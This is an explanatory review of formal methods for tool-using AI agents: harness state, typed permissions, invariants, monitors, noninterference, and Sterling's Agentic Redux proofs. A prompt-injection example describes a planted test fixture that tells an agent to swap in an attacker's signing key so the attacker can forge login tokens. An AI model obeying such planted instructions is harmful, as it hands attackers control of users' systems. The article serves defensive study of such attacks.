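# Formal specification of state, memory and permissions in tool-using AI agents

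## What the state of a tool-using agent consists of

A tool-using AI agent is a language model inside ordinary software that turns some of the model's output into actions, such as reading a file, running a command or sending an email. Engineers call that software the harness. It assembles the text the model reads, runs the tools, stores anything that must last beyond a single exchange, and often determines which actions need a person's approval.

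A formal specification of a tool-using agent defines, in a notation with an exact meaning, which states the system may be in and which steps may lead from one state to the next. Engineers have long written such specifications for network protocols, databases and operating-system kernels. Agents are harder to specify because nobody can write such a description of the language model itself, and because the text the model reads often comes from strangers. How much a specification can cover depends on what "state" includes in an agent, and the easiest way to see this is to follow one action from start to finish.

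### One tool call from start to finish

*Authority Is Not a String* (Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev, 2026) opens with a developer who asks a coding agent to fix the failing tests in an authentication module. A coordinating agent assigns one sub-agent to run the tests and another to edit the source code. Suppose the sub-agent that runs the tests has just received its subtask.

The harness first builds a prompt. *Agents' Last Exam* (2026) documents a harness that composes its standing instructions from six blocks: the agent's persona, memory from earlier sessions, usage notes for the tools, facts about the machine, behavioural rules, and instructions for particular skills. The harness adds the conversation so far. The model reads all of this as one sequence and returns text, part of which names a tool and its arguments in a fixed format. In this example, the tool is the command shell and the argument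 is the command `pytest tests/auth`. Bouras and colleagues call this output a tool proposal, an apt term because the command has not run yet and only the harness can run it.

The harness then checks the command. In CapScope, which Bouras and colleagues built, the harness splits the command into segments, rejects embedded substitutions, and compares each segment with the command prefixes that this agent may use (plus a few harmless-looking ones for reading and navigation). The test command passes, but it would fail with a `curl` upload chained onto it unless somebody had granted `curl`. If the check succeeds, the harness runs the command and appends the output to the conversation; otherwise, it appends a refusal. It then calls the model again with the longer text.

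*Towards the Harness of Embodied Agents* (2026) names the units of this loop. A turn is one model call plus the tool execution it requests. A task consists of one or more turns and ends when the model returns no tool call. The harness then consolidates the record into durable memory. A session is one continuous engagement with the user, during which tasks follow one another and messages accumulate. Because a harness can put durable memory into a later prompt, the output of a single test run can influence the agent long after the task ends.

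Real harnesses have more parts than this. *What makes a harness a harness* (2026) lists a tool registry, a context manager, memory, the loop, a verifier that checks whether the task succeeded, retry logic, an audit record, safety limits, and ordinary code for steps too sensitive to leave to the model. Several of these are optional, but the loop and the context manager are required. A system without a loop answers once and stops, and the loop soon produces more output than the prompt can hold unless some rule determines what goes back into it.

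### Activations, text and stored records

*Thinking Machines* (Asperti, Naibo and Sacerdoti Coen, 2026), a review of mathematical reasoning in language models, defines the state of a computation as all the information that characterizes its status at a given instant. For an agent in the middle of a task, that information is stored in three quite different places.

Some of an agent's state is in the model's *activations*, the numbers that the network computes as it processes the prompt. Asperti and colleagues observe that a transformer, the standard architecture for language models, may encode state implicitly in these numbers, but spreads it across all the tokens (word fragments) of the text and doesn't keep it in a persistent structure. They raise the question, for the whole field, of whether this amounts to tracking a state or only to imitating how people write about one. Activations are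 hard to specify in practice because nobody has a list of what they may mean, and they have far too many possible values to enumerate. They also don't last. A server may cache them to save time, but it can recompute them from the same text.

The *context*, meaning the prompt plus whatever the model has generated so far, holds state as prose, such as "two tests still fail" or "the user said I may edit the source folder". Such sentences can be true, out of date, or planted by somebody else, and the text alone doesn't show which. Harnesses also rewrite the context when it grows too long, usually by replacing old messages with a summary. All five coding agents examined in *Don't Blame the Large Language Model* (2026) do this, and a summary can omit a detail that a later step needs.

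Everything else is *harness state*, which consists of the memory store, the permissions, the credentials and the log. It is stored in ordinary data structures and persists between model calls. O'Connor (2026), in *Self-Programmed Execution for Language Model Agents*, remarks that the harness gives the model "the appearance of statefulness" by keeping this state across turns. Among the five coding agents, Codex and Qwen Code append session records to text files, Gemini CLI writes JSON files, OpenCode uses a small SQL database, and OpenHands CLI stores a sequence of events.

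*Always-On Agents* (Ding, Nannapaneni et al., 2026) surveys agents whose stored state carries over from one task to the next. It argues that "memory" is too narrow a word for this state, because a lapsed consent, a half-finished purchase or a cached access token shapes the next action just as a remembered fact does. It models each stored item as a record with eight fields: the value, the authority under which it may influence actions, its scope, whether and how it may change, its provenance, a link to the decisions it affected, the kind of thing it is (evidence, preference, policy, skill or commitment), and a timestamp. The survey finds that most memory systems explicitly represent only the value. Of the 435 works it coded, 72 deal with authority and 27 offer any form of rollback. The corpus is presented as a map of the field, not a census, so the imbalance matters more than the exact counts.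 A payment already sent is outside the agent's stored state, and the harness can only keep a record of it.

The effect of an instruction depends on where it is stored. An instruction in a project file never to touch the deployment scripts ends up in the context, where it may well influence the model but cannot block the action. *Towards Portable Specification of the Agent Harness* (2026) distinguishes guidance that the model can see from an enforced permission, and states that a mandatory check needs a control outside the model's discretion. A permission in the strict sense is a rule, held by the harness, that allows a named action on a named resource. Harnesses commonly sort actions into those they allow automatically, those that need the user's approval, and those they prohibit.

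### Prompt injection

Another weakness of the context is that it mixes text from different authors. *AgentSecBench* (2026) represents the model's input as a plain concatenation of trusted instructions and untrusted observations. An application may describe the boundary between them in words, but the model's next token still depends on both.

In the failing-tests example, an attacker has planted a test fixture that prints an official-looking note that a signing key has rotated and that the key in `src/auth/keys.py` must be replaced with a supplied value to restore the build. The attacker chose that value and can forge login tokens once it is in place. This is prompt injection, text in a document, message or tool result that steers the model away from its user's task. *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* (2026) explains that it works because an agent cannot reliably tell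 the user's instructions from instructions inside the data it reads. A filter that looks for bad patterns has little to detect, because the note contains no suspicious command and names an ordinary source file.

Bouras and colleagues tested four channels besides test output: project documentation, instruction files that load automatically, skill files, and comments in source code. In *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems*, Ji, Wu and colleagues (2026) derive the channels from a formal model by asking what an attacker could put into each kind of message in the system. Besides tool results, they identify the user's own query (when the user is malicious), documents from a retrieval database, messages between agents, and actions by untrusted third-party agents.

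CapScope limits what an agent can do after an injected instruction has fooled the model. The agent that runs the tests has no permission to write source files, so the harness blocks the key replacement even if the note persuades the model. Bouras and colleagues ran five Python repair tasks with five injection channels and three trials each, for 75 attacked runs per condition. The attacker's action succeeded in 3 runs (4%) under CapScope and in 33 to 47 (44 to 63%) under the baselines, which gave agents either the user's full privileges or one policy for the whole task. CapScope completed 68 of 75 repairs and the baselines 68 to 72, so the restriction had little effect on repair rates in these tasks. Five small tasks on one coding agent are not much to generalize from. CapScope also cannot stop an injected instruction that stays within the permissions of the agent reading it.

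### Types and transitions

To reason about permissions of this sort, one first has to fix what they can be. Programmers do that with algebraic data types, which build a type out of alternatives and combinations. Three lines, adapted from the schematic code of Bouras and colleagues, are enough for an example:

```
type Effect     = Read | Write | Exec
type Scope      = PathPrefix(Text) | CommandPrefixes(List of List of Text)
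type Permission = { effect: Effect, scope: Scope }
```

`Effect` and `Scope` are sum types, so each value is exactly one of the alternatives. `Permission` is a product type because each value contains both an effect and a scope. The names "sum" and "product" come from how the possible values are counted. `Effect` has three values, so with ten possible scopes, there would be 3 × 10 = 30 possible permissions.

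The definition rules out a permission with the effect "delete everything", because the type has no such value. It still allows some meaningless permissions, such as an `Exec` permission whose scope is a file path, and other code has to catch those. A tighter definition would make `Permission` a sum type, with `Read` and `Write` each carrying a path and `Exec` carrying command prefixes, so that the bad combination could not exist. Much of the craft of specification is moving checks into the types in this way.

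Sum types also help with control flow. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (2025) defines an agent's planner by cases over four kinds of message. The planner queries the model after a user message or a tool result, makes the requested call after a tool-call message, and finishes after a final answer. Because the list of message kinds is closed, a compiler can warn a programmer who forgets to handle one.

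Types describe the states, and a state machine adds the movement between them. It consists of a set of states *S*, a set of events *E* and a transition function δ : *S* × *E* → *S*, which takes the current state and an event and returns the next state. *MarkovSim* (2026), an agent harness for long engineering simulations, governs each step of its execution agent with a machine small enough to print (after a question to the engineer, the agent resumes with the reply):

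| State | Event | Next state |
|---|---|---|
| GENERATION | the agent has produced its modelling operations | VERIFICATION |
| VERIFICATION | a check fails | REFINEMENT |
| REFINEMENT | revised operations are ready | VERIFICATION |
| VERIFICATION | the agent needs the engineer | ASK_HUMAN |
| any | the agent itself fails | EXCEPTION |

The machine guarantees an order of work in which both new and revised operations go to verification. Its five states cannot represent whether those operations are any good.

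A machine for the whole agent needs a richer state. Ji and colleagues use the context of every agent, the tool calls now pending, and the latest replies; their events are user queries, tool results and retrieved documents, and a round ends when no agent issues a new call. O'Connor's version is more compact. His "agentic machine" has a state space *S*, a prompt function *p* that turns a state into a prompt, and a harness function *h* that takes a state and the model's completion and returns the next state. With *M* for the model, one turn is

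*c* = *M*(*p*(*s*)),  *s*′ = *h*(*s*, *c*).

All the uncertainty about the model is in *M*, which may give different answers to the same prompt. The harness function *h* is an ordinary program. O'Connor includes tool execution in *h*, whereas Ji and colleagues treat each tool result as an external event. Treating results as external is often more convenient in a specification, because the contents of a web page are no more predictable than a model's output.

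### Properties of states and of runs

A state machine makes it possible to specify precisely what should never happen. An *invariant* is a statement that must hold in every state the system can reach, such as "no sub-agent holds a permission broader than the limit set for the whole task".

A *trace* is the ordered sequence of calls and results in one run. For example, the calls might run the tests, read the parser, edit it and run the tests again. *DART* (2026), which studies how agents recover from failed steps, records each step as the state before, the action, the state after and the change in memory. An *action log* is a trace stored in append-only form.

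A *monitor* is trusted code that checks each proposed call before it runs and can refuse it. CapScope's monitor is a function that the coding agent Pi invokes before every tool call and that can return "block". Bouras and colleagues note that a hook that only observes calls is not sufficient, because the file may be gone by the time it sees the call. A monitor also sees only the current run so far, which limits the properties it can enforce.

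A *label* is a mark on a stored value that records how secret the value is or how trustworthy its origin is. For example, a downloaded web page is labeled "untrusted", and so is the summary that a model writes from it. The survey *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026) connects current work on labels to Denning's 1976 research on information flow. In *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, the basic rule gives a model's response the combined label of everything the model read, which is safe but often too strict. *APPA* (2026) orders its labels by restrictiveness, and an agent's label can only become more restrictive as data comes in. An agent that has read one dubious email could therefore lose its more sensitive tools for the rest of the run. This is why agents need *endorsement*, a decision that raises an untrusted value to trusted status. In *PerMIT* (2026), a system for protecting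 agent memory, a gate shows a person the exact bytes and their destination, and the person's approval applies only to those bytes.

*Noninterference* is the strictest of these ideas. SRI, whose computer scientists developed the theory, explains that one security domain is noninterfering with another if no action by the first can influence what is later visible to the second. Under this property, an agent must make the same payments in two runs that differ only in the body of one untrusted email. Unlike an invariant, noninterference is defined by comparing two runs, so examining a single state cannot show that it holds.

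A model that reads the email offers no such guarantee, since any word in its input may change its output. The harness can provide one by controlling what the model sees or what its output can do. *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026) proves a noninterference theorem for a small programming language that represents harness code and the plans a model writes. The guarantee holds even for a fully compromised model, provided that the plan endorses nothing and the tool library labels its sources correctly and checks labels wherever data could do damage. The protection weakens once a plan endorses untrusted data, and both attacks that succeeded in the paper's tests relied on such an endorsement.

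### Specifying, proving, checking and monitoring

Writers on agent safety sometimes use "formally verified" for several different activities. CapScope is small enough to show them apart.

Its specification has three rules. Mint creates permissions from trusted input before the agent has read any project file. Derive gives a sub-agent only the requested permissions that are no broader than an entry in the delegating agent's limit. Invoke runs a tool call only if a permission already in the caller's store covers it. These rules define what the code should do, but they don't prove that the running code does it.

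A *proof* is an argument that covers every state the rules can produce, however many there are. The usual method is to show that an invariant holds at the start and that each rule preserves it. Here Mint sets the limit on permissions, Derive can only narrow them, and Invoke doesn't change them, so no agent ever exceeds what the trusted input granted. Bouras and colleagues argue this by inspecting the rules. For larger systems, researchers use proof assistants, which are programs that check every step of such an argument.

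In *model checking*, a program explores every reachable state of a finite version of the system, such as one with three agents and five files. It either reports that the invariant held in every state or returns a trace that violates it. (The "model" is the finite description, not a language model.) This method needs no clever argument, but its result applies only to the version searched.

*Monitoring at run time* examines one run as it happens and requires no information about other possible runs. A bug in the monitor may go unnoticed until a bad call gets through.

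All of this depends on a *trusted base*, meaning everything that must work correctly for a proof to apply to the running system. For CapScope, this includes the assumptions that every effect passes through the check, that each agent's permissions stay separate, that the code comparing paths and commands is correct, and that only the host can create permissions. The CapScope paper acknowledges that its rules have limits. Permission to run `pytest` is also permission to run whatever project code `pytest` imports, including code an attacker wrote. The search command `grep` may look at files outside an agent's reading scope. Neither case breaks a rule, so the deployment still needs a sandbox.

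### The model as an unknown source of proposals

Formal specification of agents is older than language models. *Structuring a Z Specification to Provide a Formal Framework* (Luck and d'Inverno, 1995) uses Z, a notation built on sets and logic, to define an agent as an object with goals, whose state includes the history of its actions and the actions it will perform next. *Engineering AgentSpeak(L)* (d'Inverno and Luck, 1998) gives a strongly typed model of a programming language whose agents work from beliefs, desires and intentions. A specifier could list the beliefs and plans of such an agent because a programmer had written them.

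A language model has no such list, but the 1995 framework suggests an alternative. It leaves open how an agent chooses its actions and requires only that they lie within the set the agent is capable of. Current work constrains the language model in much the same way. *PerMIT* treats it as an arbitrary strategy over its observations, its history and random coin flips, and the harness does not inspect its reasoning. *APPA* assumes that the model may propose any tool call. In *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies* (2026), the model's replies come from an oracle, a formal stand-in for an outside source of answers, so a conventional algorithm or a person typing at a terminal could replace the model without changing the definitions.

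The specification therefore covers the harness and treats the model as an unknown source of proposed calls. A theorem proved this way still holds if the model is replaced or an injection succeeds, because the proof does not assume that the model behaves correctly. However, the theorem does not show whether the proposed calls are any good. A harness that refuses every call satisfies most safety invariants, so experiments have to report completed tasks as well as blocked attacks.

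The boundary of the harness is partly a design choice. O'Connor built a system in which the model writes the program that decides what the next prompt will contain, which is normally the harness's job. He proves that, from a suitable starting state, the model can reproduce any computable agent loop, so a specification of the loop would constrain very little. But the model's programs still run in an external runtime, and the user decides whether functions that read or write files are available there, so permissions can stay outside the model even when the loop moves into its output.

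## Agentic Redux: typed state changed by a single function

A harness that stores its state in ordinary data structures can still end up in a state that nobody intended. The data type determines how many such states are possible. Suppose an agent is allowed to spend a company's money. A spending request starts as Idle and becomes Proposed when the agent asks for an amount. The harness then makes it Approved or Rejected, and an Approved request becomes Executed once the payment goes through.

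### Sixteen patterns or five

Many programs would store such a request as a record with four optional fields:

```
type Proposal = { amount: Integer, purpose: Text }

type Request  = { proposal:  Optional Proposal,
                  approval:  Optional Approval,
                  receipt:   Optional Receipt,
                  rejection: Optional Text }
```

Each of the four fields is either present or absent, so the record allows 16 patterns, of which five make sense. An Idle request has none of the fields, and a Proposed request has only a proposal. An Approved request has a proposal and an approval, and an Executed request also has a receipt. A Rejected request has a proposal and a rejection. The other eleven patterns include a receipt without an approval, which means that money left the account without anyone agreeing to it, and a request that is both approved and rejected. Programmers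 have to check for these cases in every function that reads a request or assume that they never occur.

A sum type with five constructors, one for each alternative, leaves no room for them:

```
type Request = Idle
             | Proposed(Proposal)
             | Approved(Proposal, Approval)
             | Executed(Proposal, Approval, Receipt)
             | Rejected(Proposal, Text)
```

A program cannot build an Executed request without supplying an approval, because the constructor requires one. But the type doesn't prevent the approval from belonging to some other proposal, or a carelessly written program from replacing a Rejected request with an Executed one. Only four of the 20 possible moves from one constructor to a different one are legitimate here, so something besides the type has to control the moves.

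### How two reasonable decisions overspend

The next difficulty appears with more than one agent. Aaron Sterling's June 2026 paper, *Provably Auditable and Safe LLM Agents from Human-Authored Ontologies*, opens with an example in which two agents share a budget of $100,000. Agent A can spend $45,000 or nothing, and agent B $60,000 or nothing. Each sees only its own part of the state and decides independently. Either purchase alone fits the budget, but together they cost $105,000.

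Showing each agent the running total doesn't help if both read it before either writes. Agent A reads a total of 0 and concludes that $45,000 fits, while Agent B reads the same total and concludes that $60,000 fits. Both then record their spending, each having followed the rule based on the total it read. Sterling calls this *write skew*, a term from Berenson and colleagues' 1995 critique of database standards. In write skew, two processes read overlapping data, write to different records, and together break a rule that neither would have broken alone.

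Write skew is easy to confuse with a *lost update*, in which one process overwrites another's change to the same record. Lost updates are fairly common among agents. In the *S-Bus* (2026) microbenchmark, four agents wrote to one shared key, and silent overwrites occurred in all 20 trials. But a check for overwritten records would miss the write skew in the budget example, because both records survive intact.

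Ordinary databases can have the same gap, depending on their configuration. *TOKI* (2026), which studies contradictions in agents' persistent memory, tested both kinds of conflict on PostgreSQL 17.10. At the "repeatable read" setting, the database blocked every lost update by aborting the losing writer, but write skew still occurred in all 30 runs, as it did at the weaker "read committed" setting. Only the strictest setting, "serializable", prevented write skew, by aborting one of the two writers each time. An engineer who tests only for lost updates could therefore wrongly conclude that "repeatable read" prevents both kinds of conflict.

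*CoAgent* (2026) defines serializability for agents to mean that any concurrent run is equivalent to some run in which the agents act one after another. This would fix the budget example as long as both agents check the total, but if an agent never checks, two purchases made in turn can still add up to $105,000.

### One function that decides

The remedy is to take the decision away from the agents. They may only ask, and one transition function answers:

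```
type State = { requests: one Request per agent,  log: List of Entry }

committed(s) = sum of the amounts in all Approved and Executed requests

step(s, event) = case (the agent's request, event) of
    (Idle,           Propose p)  ->  Proposed(p)
    (Proposed(p),    Decide a)   ->  if committed(s) + p.amount <= 100000
                                     then Approved(p, a)
                                     else Rejected(p, "over budget")
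    (Approved(p, a), Paid r)     ->  Executed(p, a, r)
    anything else                ->  leave the request as it is
```

In every case, `step` also appends one entry to the log with the event and its outcome. The first three lines contain the four legitimate moves, and the last line blocks the rest. With the two agents from the example, a run looks like this:

| Event | Committed before | Outcome in the log | Committed after |
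|---|---|---|---|
| A proposes $45,000 | $0 | Proposed | $0 |
| B proposes $60,000 | $0 | Proposed | $0 |
| decision on A | $0 | Approved | $45,000 |
| decision on B | $45,000 | Rejected, over budget | $45,000 |

If B's request had come up first, B would have received its $60,000 and A would have received nothing. The function guarantees that spending stays within the budget, but it does not allocate the money by merit.

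The budget invariant is the statement committed(*s*) ≤ 100,000. The proof that it holds in every reachable state is an *induction* over transitions.

Every request starts Idle, so the committed total starts at 0. Suppose the total is at most 100,000 in some state *s*, and `step` processes one event. If `step` leaves the request alone, the total stays the same. It also stays the same if a request moves from Idle to Proposed or from Proposed to Rejected, because requests in those states don't count towards it. If a request moves from Approved to Executed, the total doesn't change because the request's amount counts in both states. The only other move, from Proposed to Approved, raises the total to committed(*s*) + *p*.amount, and `step` makes that move only after checking that this sum is at most 100,000. So the invariant still holds after one step, and by induction it holds after any number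 of steps.

The proof holds regardless of why B proposed $60,000, even if the cause was an injected instruction. It assumes that only `step` changes the state and that `step` finishes processing one event before starting the next. If two copies of `step` both read the same old state, the write skew would return.

Functional programmers call `step` a *reducer*, and running it over a list of events a *fold*. The fold applies `step` to an initial state and the first event, then to the resulting state and the second event, and so on to the end of the list. *V12 — Stateless Reducer*, a description of the pattern for agent builders, traces it to the web library Redux, the language Elm and a guideline of the 12-Factor Agents framework ("make your agent a stateless reducer"). The practical reason to use the pattern is to avoid hidden state. If a running process keeps information that never reaches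 the store, a restored copy will silently behave differently, and nobody can reproduce the resulting bug from the recorded inputs.

A language model can answer the same prompt differently the second time, so calling it again during a replay could change the result of the fold. The usual solution is to record the model's answers and treat them as inputs. In *The Log is the Agent* (2026), an agent's state is a deterministic fold over an append-only log of events, and a cache stores every model and tool response. A replay reads from the cache, makes no new model calls, and reproduces the run byte for byte.

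### Slices, proposals and a meta-agent

Sterling's architecture, Agentic Redux, applies this pattern to several agents at once. It is named after Redux, a small library for managing the state of web applications. Dan Abramov wrote Redux so that a page would always show the current state. If a user ticks a box in one browser tab, the box should also be ticked in another tab showing the same page. In Redux, the visible components only display data, and all changes go through one place that holds the whole state.

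In Agentic Redux, the components are agents. The global state is a record of named fields, and each agent has a role that determines which fields it can see. In Sterling's method for deriving the roles, the designer lists the tasks in the domain and the fields each task reads or writes, groups the tasks whose fields largely overlap, and assigns each group to one role. The fields used by a role's tasks form its *slice* of the state. If a role has a field that none of its tasks needs, the grouping was too coarse.

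The main parts have these types, lightly simplified from the paper:

```
agent     : Slice × Responses      -> Action
mutate    : State × Action × Time  -> State
invariant : State                  -> Pass | Reject(Text) | Escalate(Text)
```

An agent is a function that takes its slice and the responses from the model and tools, and returns a proposed action. Agents cannot send each other messages, so one agent can influence another only through a change that has passed adjudication. An experiment in *Verified Detection and Prevention of Concurrency Anomalies* (2026) suggests why this restriction is useful. It ran 900 sessions with the model gpt-4o under three kinds of concurrency control. Under snapshot isolation, which checks an operation for conflicts only if it writes something, in 3% of the sessions with a read-only triage agent, that agent's decision reached other agents unchecked. The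 rate depends on that set-up, but the same thing can happen wherever agents can pass on conclusions without writing them to the shared state.

The *meta-agent* adjudicates the proposals. Despite the name, it is an ordinary function and not a language model. It applies `mutate` to produce a candidate state, without installing it. It then runs the invariants on the candidate in a fixed order and stops at the first one that fails. If that invariant returned Reject, the state stays as it was, and the ledger receives an entry that names the invariant and the reason. Escalate does the same and also puts the proposal in a queue for a human. If every invariant passes, the candidate becomes the new state and the ledger records an approval. (A refused proposal therefore exists only in the ledger, whereas the spending example stores it as a Rejected request.)

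The check examines the state that the action would produce, so it also catches errors in `mutate`. Suppose a bug makes `mutate` add an extra zero to the amount. A check on the proposal alone would approve the $5,000, but the meta-agent checks a candidate state with $50,000 more committed and refuses if that breaks the budget. Sterling contrasts this with the common practice of asking a language model whether a change is acceptable and following its recommendation, which offers no guarantee.

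Sterling developed the architecture for a more complicated problem than a budget. AHCCCS, Arizona's Medicaid agency, limits how many definitive urine drug tests it pays for. A patient whose last positive test was more than 90 days ago may have three in 90 days, while a patient within 30 days of a positive test may have only one every seven days. In Sterling's example, a patient named David is in the first group and tests negative on a definitive test on 23 March. On 26 March, a cheaper presumptive test detects opioids, and the provider orders a definitive test to confirm the result. AHCCCS won't pay for it, because the positive presumptive test has moved David into the stricter group.

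A billing agent with yesterday's information would count a test as the second of three permitted and approve it. The billing agent's slice holds the claim history and the clinical agent's slice holds the patient's group, so neither can evaluate the coverage rule alone. The paper calls such a rule a *cross-cutting invariant*. The second domain, security vulnerability disclosure, has four proposing agents and nine invariants. One invariant limits how many reports a software maintainer receives within a set period across all vulnerabilities, but the agent that tracks patches sees only one vulnerability at a time.

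### The two theorems

Theorem 1 generalizes the budget proof to any domain that supplies the parts above. If the initial state satisfies the invariants, so does every domain state that the run reaches, whatever well-typed program drives the system and whatever sequence of responses the models and tools return. Because that sequence also determines which agent goes next, the theorem covers every order in which competing proposals might arrive.

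The proof has the same form as the one for the budget. The initial state satisfies the invariants by assumption. Only the approval rule changes the domain state, and it installs a candidate only if the candidate satisfies every invariant. No run can therefore have write skew, because Sterling defines a write-skew run as one that reaches a state violating a cross-cutting invariant.

By Theorem 2, each adjudication appends exactly one entry to the ledger, no other step appends any, and no step alters an existing entry. Every entry records the action and its time, and entries for rejected and escalated proposals also record the invariant that failed and its message. The theorem holds even if the initial state violates the invariants, so the ledger is still a faithful record in that case.

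The entries contain less than the paper's overview suggests. There, Sterling writes that the meta-agent logs the new global state and proof that all invariants hold. In the formal definition, an approval entry has an identifier, a time, a tag and the action, with no state and no proof. An auditor can still recover the states, because `mutate` is deterministic and a fold over the approved actions reproduces them from the initial state. What the ledger cannot supply is the agent's reason for proposing the action, or evidence that the payment or disclosure then happened. Sterling leaves the handling of outside events to the harness. (LogAct, by contrast, records each action before it runs.)

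The theorems apply to a running system only under several assumptions. Every change must go through the meta-agent, and `mutate` and the invariants must be deterministic functions that always return a result. The ledger must be append-only on disk, where an administrator with the right password can edit a file. Confining agents to their slices also requires that no tool give an agent access to fields outside its slice. The formal model excludes such tools by definition, but in practice a shell command that reads the shared database would break the confinement. Sterling acknowledges that "real world software is buggy" and recommends surrounding each agent with a separate governance layer that monitors for the behaviour the types are supposed to prevent.

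Sterling reports that a language model generated about 90% of the appendix containing the proofs, that earlier versions of the proofs had errors, and that the current ones "look good to me". The paper mentions no proof assistant. The arguments for Theorems 1 and 2 are short case distinctions that a reader can check by hand, and they appear to hold. Elsewhere, the appendix contradicts itself. One passage claims that type safety rules out stuck configurations, in which no rule applies and the system cannot continue, but the type-safety theorem lists them as a possible outcome. Neither main theorem depends on that claim, but a proof assistant would have rejected it.

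### Wrong invariants and stalled systems

Sterling puts badly written invariants out of scope, since the meta-agent will enforce whatever it receives. The spending example above contains such an error, because its amounts are integers, which can be negative. If a third agent proposes to spend −$50,000, perhaps as a refund that never arrives, `step` approves it and the committed total falls to −$50,000. It then approves A's request, which brings the total to −$5,000, and B's, which brings it to $55,000. The company has now paid out $105,000 without violating the invariant. The proof is still correct, because it doesn't depend on amounts being positive. A type for amounts that excludes negative numbers would fix this particular error.

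The drug-test domain could produce a subtler failure. Suppose the meta-agent had approved David's second definitive test before anybody recorded the positive result. Recording that result now would produce a state with two tests in seven days for a patient who is allowed only one. If the coverage rule returns Reject, the meta-agent refuses to store a true fact about the patient. This happens because invariants over stored state apply to an agent's observations as well as its choices. A designer who foresees the problem can avoid it by having the rule return Escalate or apply only to new claims.

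Theorem 1 covers only the rules in the meta-agent's list. Sterling suggests in the main text that an agent can enforce a rule on its own if all the relevant fields lie within its slice, but a builder who leaves such a rule to an agent that runs on a language model has no guarantee for it. It is safer to follow the formal version, in which the meta-agent checks everything.

People still have to find the right rules, with some help from a language model. In Sterling's method, a domain expert first writes an *ontology*, a structured description of the things, processes and policies in the field. A language model then derives the agents' roles and the invariants from it. To check the result, Sterling proposes that a person follow a patient or a vulnerability step by step from start to finish, looking for any change that should be forbidden but that no invariant blocks. This is sensible, but nobody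 can prove that the search found every missing rule.

Both theorems guarantee *safety*, meaning that nothing bad happens. They don't guarantee *liveness*, meaning that the system eventually does what it should. In the formal model, the kernel selects an agent and waits for its action, so an agent that never answers stops the whole system without violating an invariant. The theorems don't cover deadlines for a similar reason. For example, an organization that publishes a cryptographic commitment to a vulnerability report must eventually reveal the report, but Sterling defers that obligation to a follow-up paper.

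### When a human overrides the invariants

The paper seems to contradict itself on human supervision. Sterling writes in the introduction that the theorems extend to a version with a human supervisor, the *counselor*, and that preservation of invariants and auditability "still hold", but writes in the threat model that humans may commit changes that violate invariants. Section 4.2 reconciles the two claims by adding a condition to Theorem 1. In the extended version, every reachable state satisfies the invariants if every change the counselor commits preserves them all, which Sterling calls a *safe counselor commit*.

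The theorem is valid but much weaker than the introduction suggests. It assumes, rather than proves, that the human's steps preserve the invariants. It therefore guarantees only that nothing else in the system breaks an invariant, and a single unsafe commit voids the theorem's conclusion.

An unsafe commit also has consequences that the paper leaves to the harness. Suppose the budget rule returns Escalate, and the counselor approves B's $60,000 on top of A's $45,000. The meta-agent checks the whole candidate state each time, so even a later proposal to correct a spelling mistake produces a candidate with $105,000 committed, fails the budget rule and goes to the counselor. If the counselor had broken a rule that returns Reject, the meta-agent would refuse later proposals until one of them repaired the state. The counselor could not step in, because the formal rules let a counselor act only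 on an escalated proposal.

The system remains auditable under human oversight without any such condition. When the counselor commits a state, the system runs every invariant on it and stores the results in the ledger, together with the counselor's identity, the new state and a reference to the escalation that led to it. A failed invariant doesn't block the commit, but the stored results let an auditor find every unsafe commit mechanically. Theorem 4 guarantees that each counselor entry refers to exactly one earlier escalation and that no two entries refer to the same one. In a supervised system, therefore, the record is always faithful, and the invariants hold as long as the humans respect them.

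The extended proof also requires all adjudication on the shared state to stop while the counselor decides, so that the decision applies to the current state. Sterling considers this realistic, since work on a vulnerability report does pause when somebody escalates it to an expert. That example involves a single report, but the limit on reports per maintainer applies across many vulnerabilities. The shared state must therefore cover them all, and one slow decision could hold up work on the others.

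### Evidence beyond the two domains

Sterling says that working code for both domains is available, and reports using the ontology method for seven problem domains and three agent architectures, including work not yet published. The paper contains no measurements, such as completion rates or counts of rejected proposals. Sterling suggests that a simple checker might be faster than a language model that judges its own proposals, but gives no timings to support this.

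As independent support, Sterling cites Risk Agents, a framework that engineers at Cash App built for financial compliance, and calls it "near-isomorphic" to Agentic Redux. This comparison rests on Sterling's reading of a set of working-group minutes. Sterling also describes Anthropic's process for disclosing vulnerabilities as having the same structure. But by Sterling's own account, Claude both proposes and decides in that process, so it lacks the separation between the two that the theorems depend on.

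*ESAA* (dos Santos Filho, 2026) is a closer match. It was published in February, four months before Sterling's paper. Its software-writing agents emit only structured intentions. A deterministic orchestrator validates them, appends events to a log, writes the files, and computes the project's current state from the log. A verification command replays the log and compares hashes, which addresses the concern about edited files that Theorem 2 leaves open. Two authors arrived at nearly the same design, which is decent evidence that it suits the problem, but not that it performs well or that anyone outside these projects can write adequate invariants for it.

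The most likely practical objection is that putting every change in a single queue would slow the agents down. *CoAgent* points out that agents may run for hours or even days, so running them one after another wastes most of the benefit of having several. Existing systems also divide the state into parts that only one agent may write, or give each agent a copy and merge the copies at the end. Agentic Redux could be less restrictive than its formal model. Theorem 1 requires the checks to happen one at a time, but not the agents' reasoning, because the meta-agent applies each proposal to the current state rather than the state the agent saw. Agents could therefore work in parallel and queue only for the check, which is quick.

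The drawback would be wasted effort, since an agent might work for an hour on a plan that another agent's purchase has already made unaffordable, and learn this only when its proposal is rejected. *Verified Detection and Prevention of Concurrency Anomalies* recommends locks for cases where a wasted model call is worse than a missed chance to work together. An agent reserves the data before reading it, and drops the operation if another agent already holds the data. *CoAgent* instead uses the language model to dismiss overlaps that don't affect the agent's plan, such as a new line that another agent has added to a log file it had scanned. That saves work but makes the result depend on the model's judgement. A builder could combine such a filter with Sterling's meta-agent, and Theorem 1 would still hold, provided that the filter only decides which proposals to abandon and the final check remains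 an ordinary function. For simple numerical limits, a harness can also divide the budget in advance and give each agent a permission that runs out as it spends, which is closer to Agenra's approach.

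## LogAct: a typed log written before each action

Agentic Redux's ledger can't show whether an approved payment went out, which matters if the machine crashes just after the approval. Databases usually solve a similar problem with *write-ahead logging*. The database writes a description of each change to durable storage before making the change. After a crash, it reads the log and either finishes the interrupted change or undoes it.

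*LogAct* (Balakrishnan, Bharambe and colleagues, 2026) applies this method to agents. The system, built at Meta, appends every action to a log before running it, and other programs can stop the action after it is logged. The database method has to be adapted because a database change has a fixed format and a known way to undo it, whereas an agent may run any code that the model writes. Much of what an agent changes is also in outside services, so the harness cannot restore everything from a snapshot.

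### Nine entry types and four components

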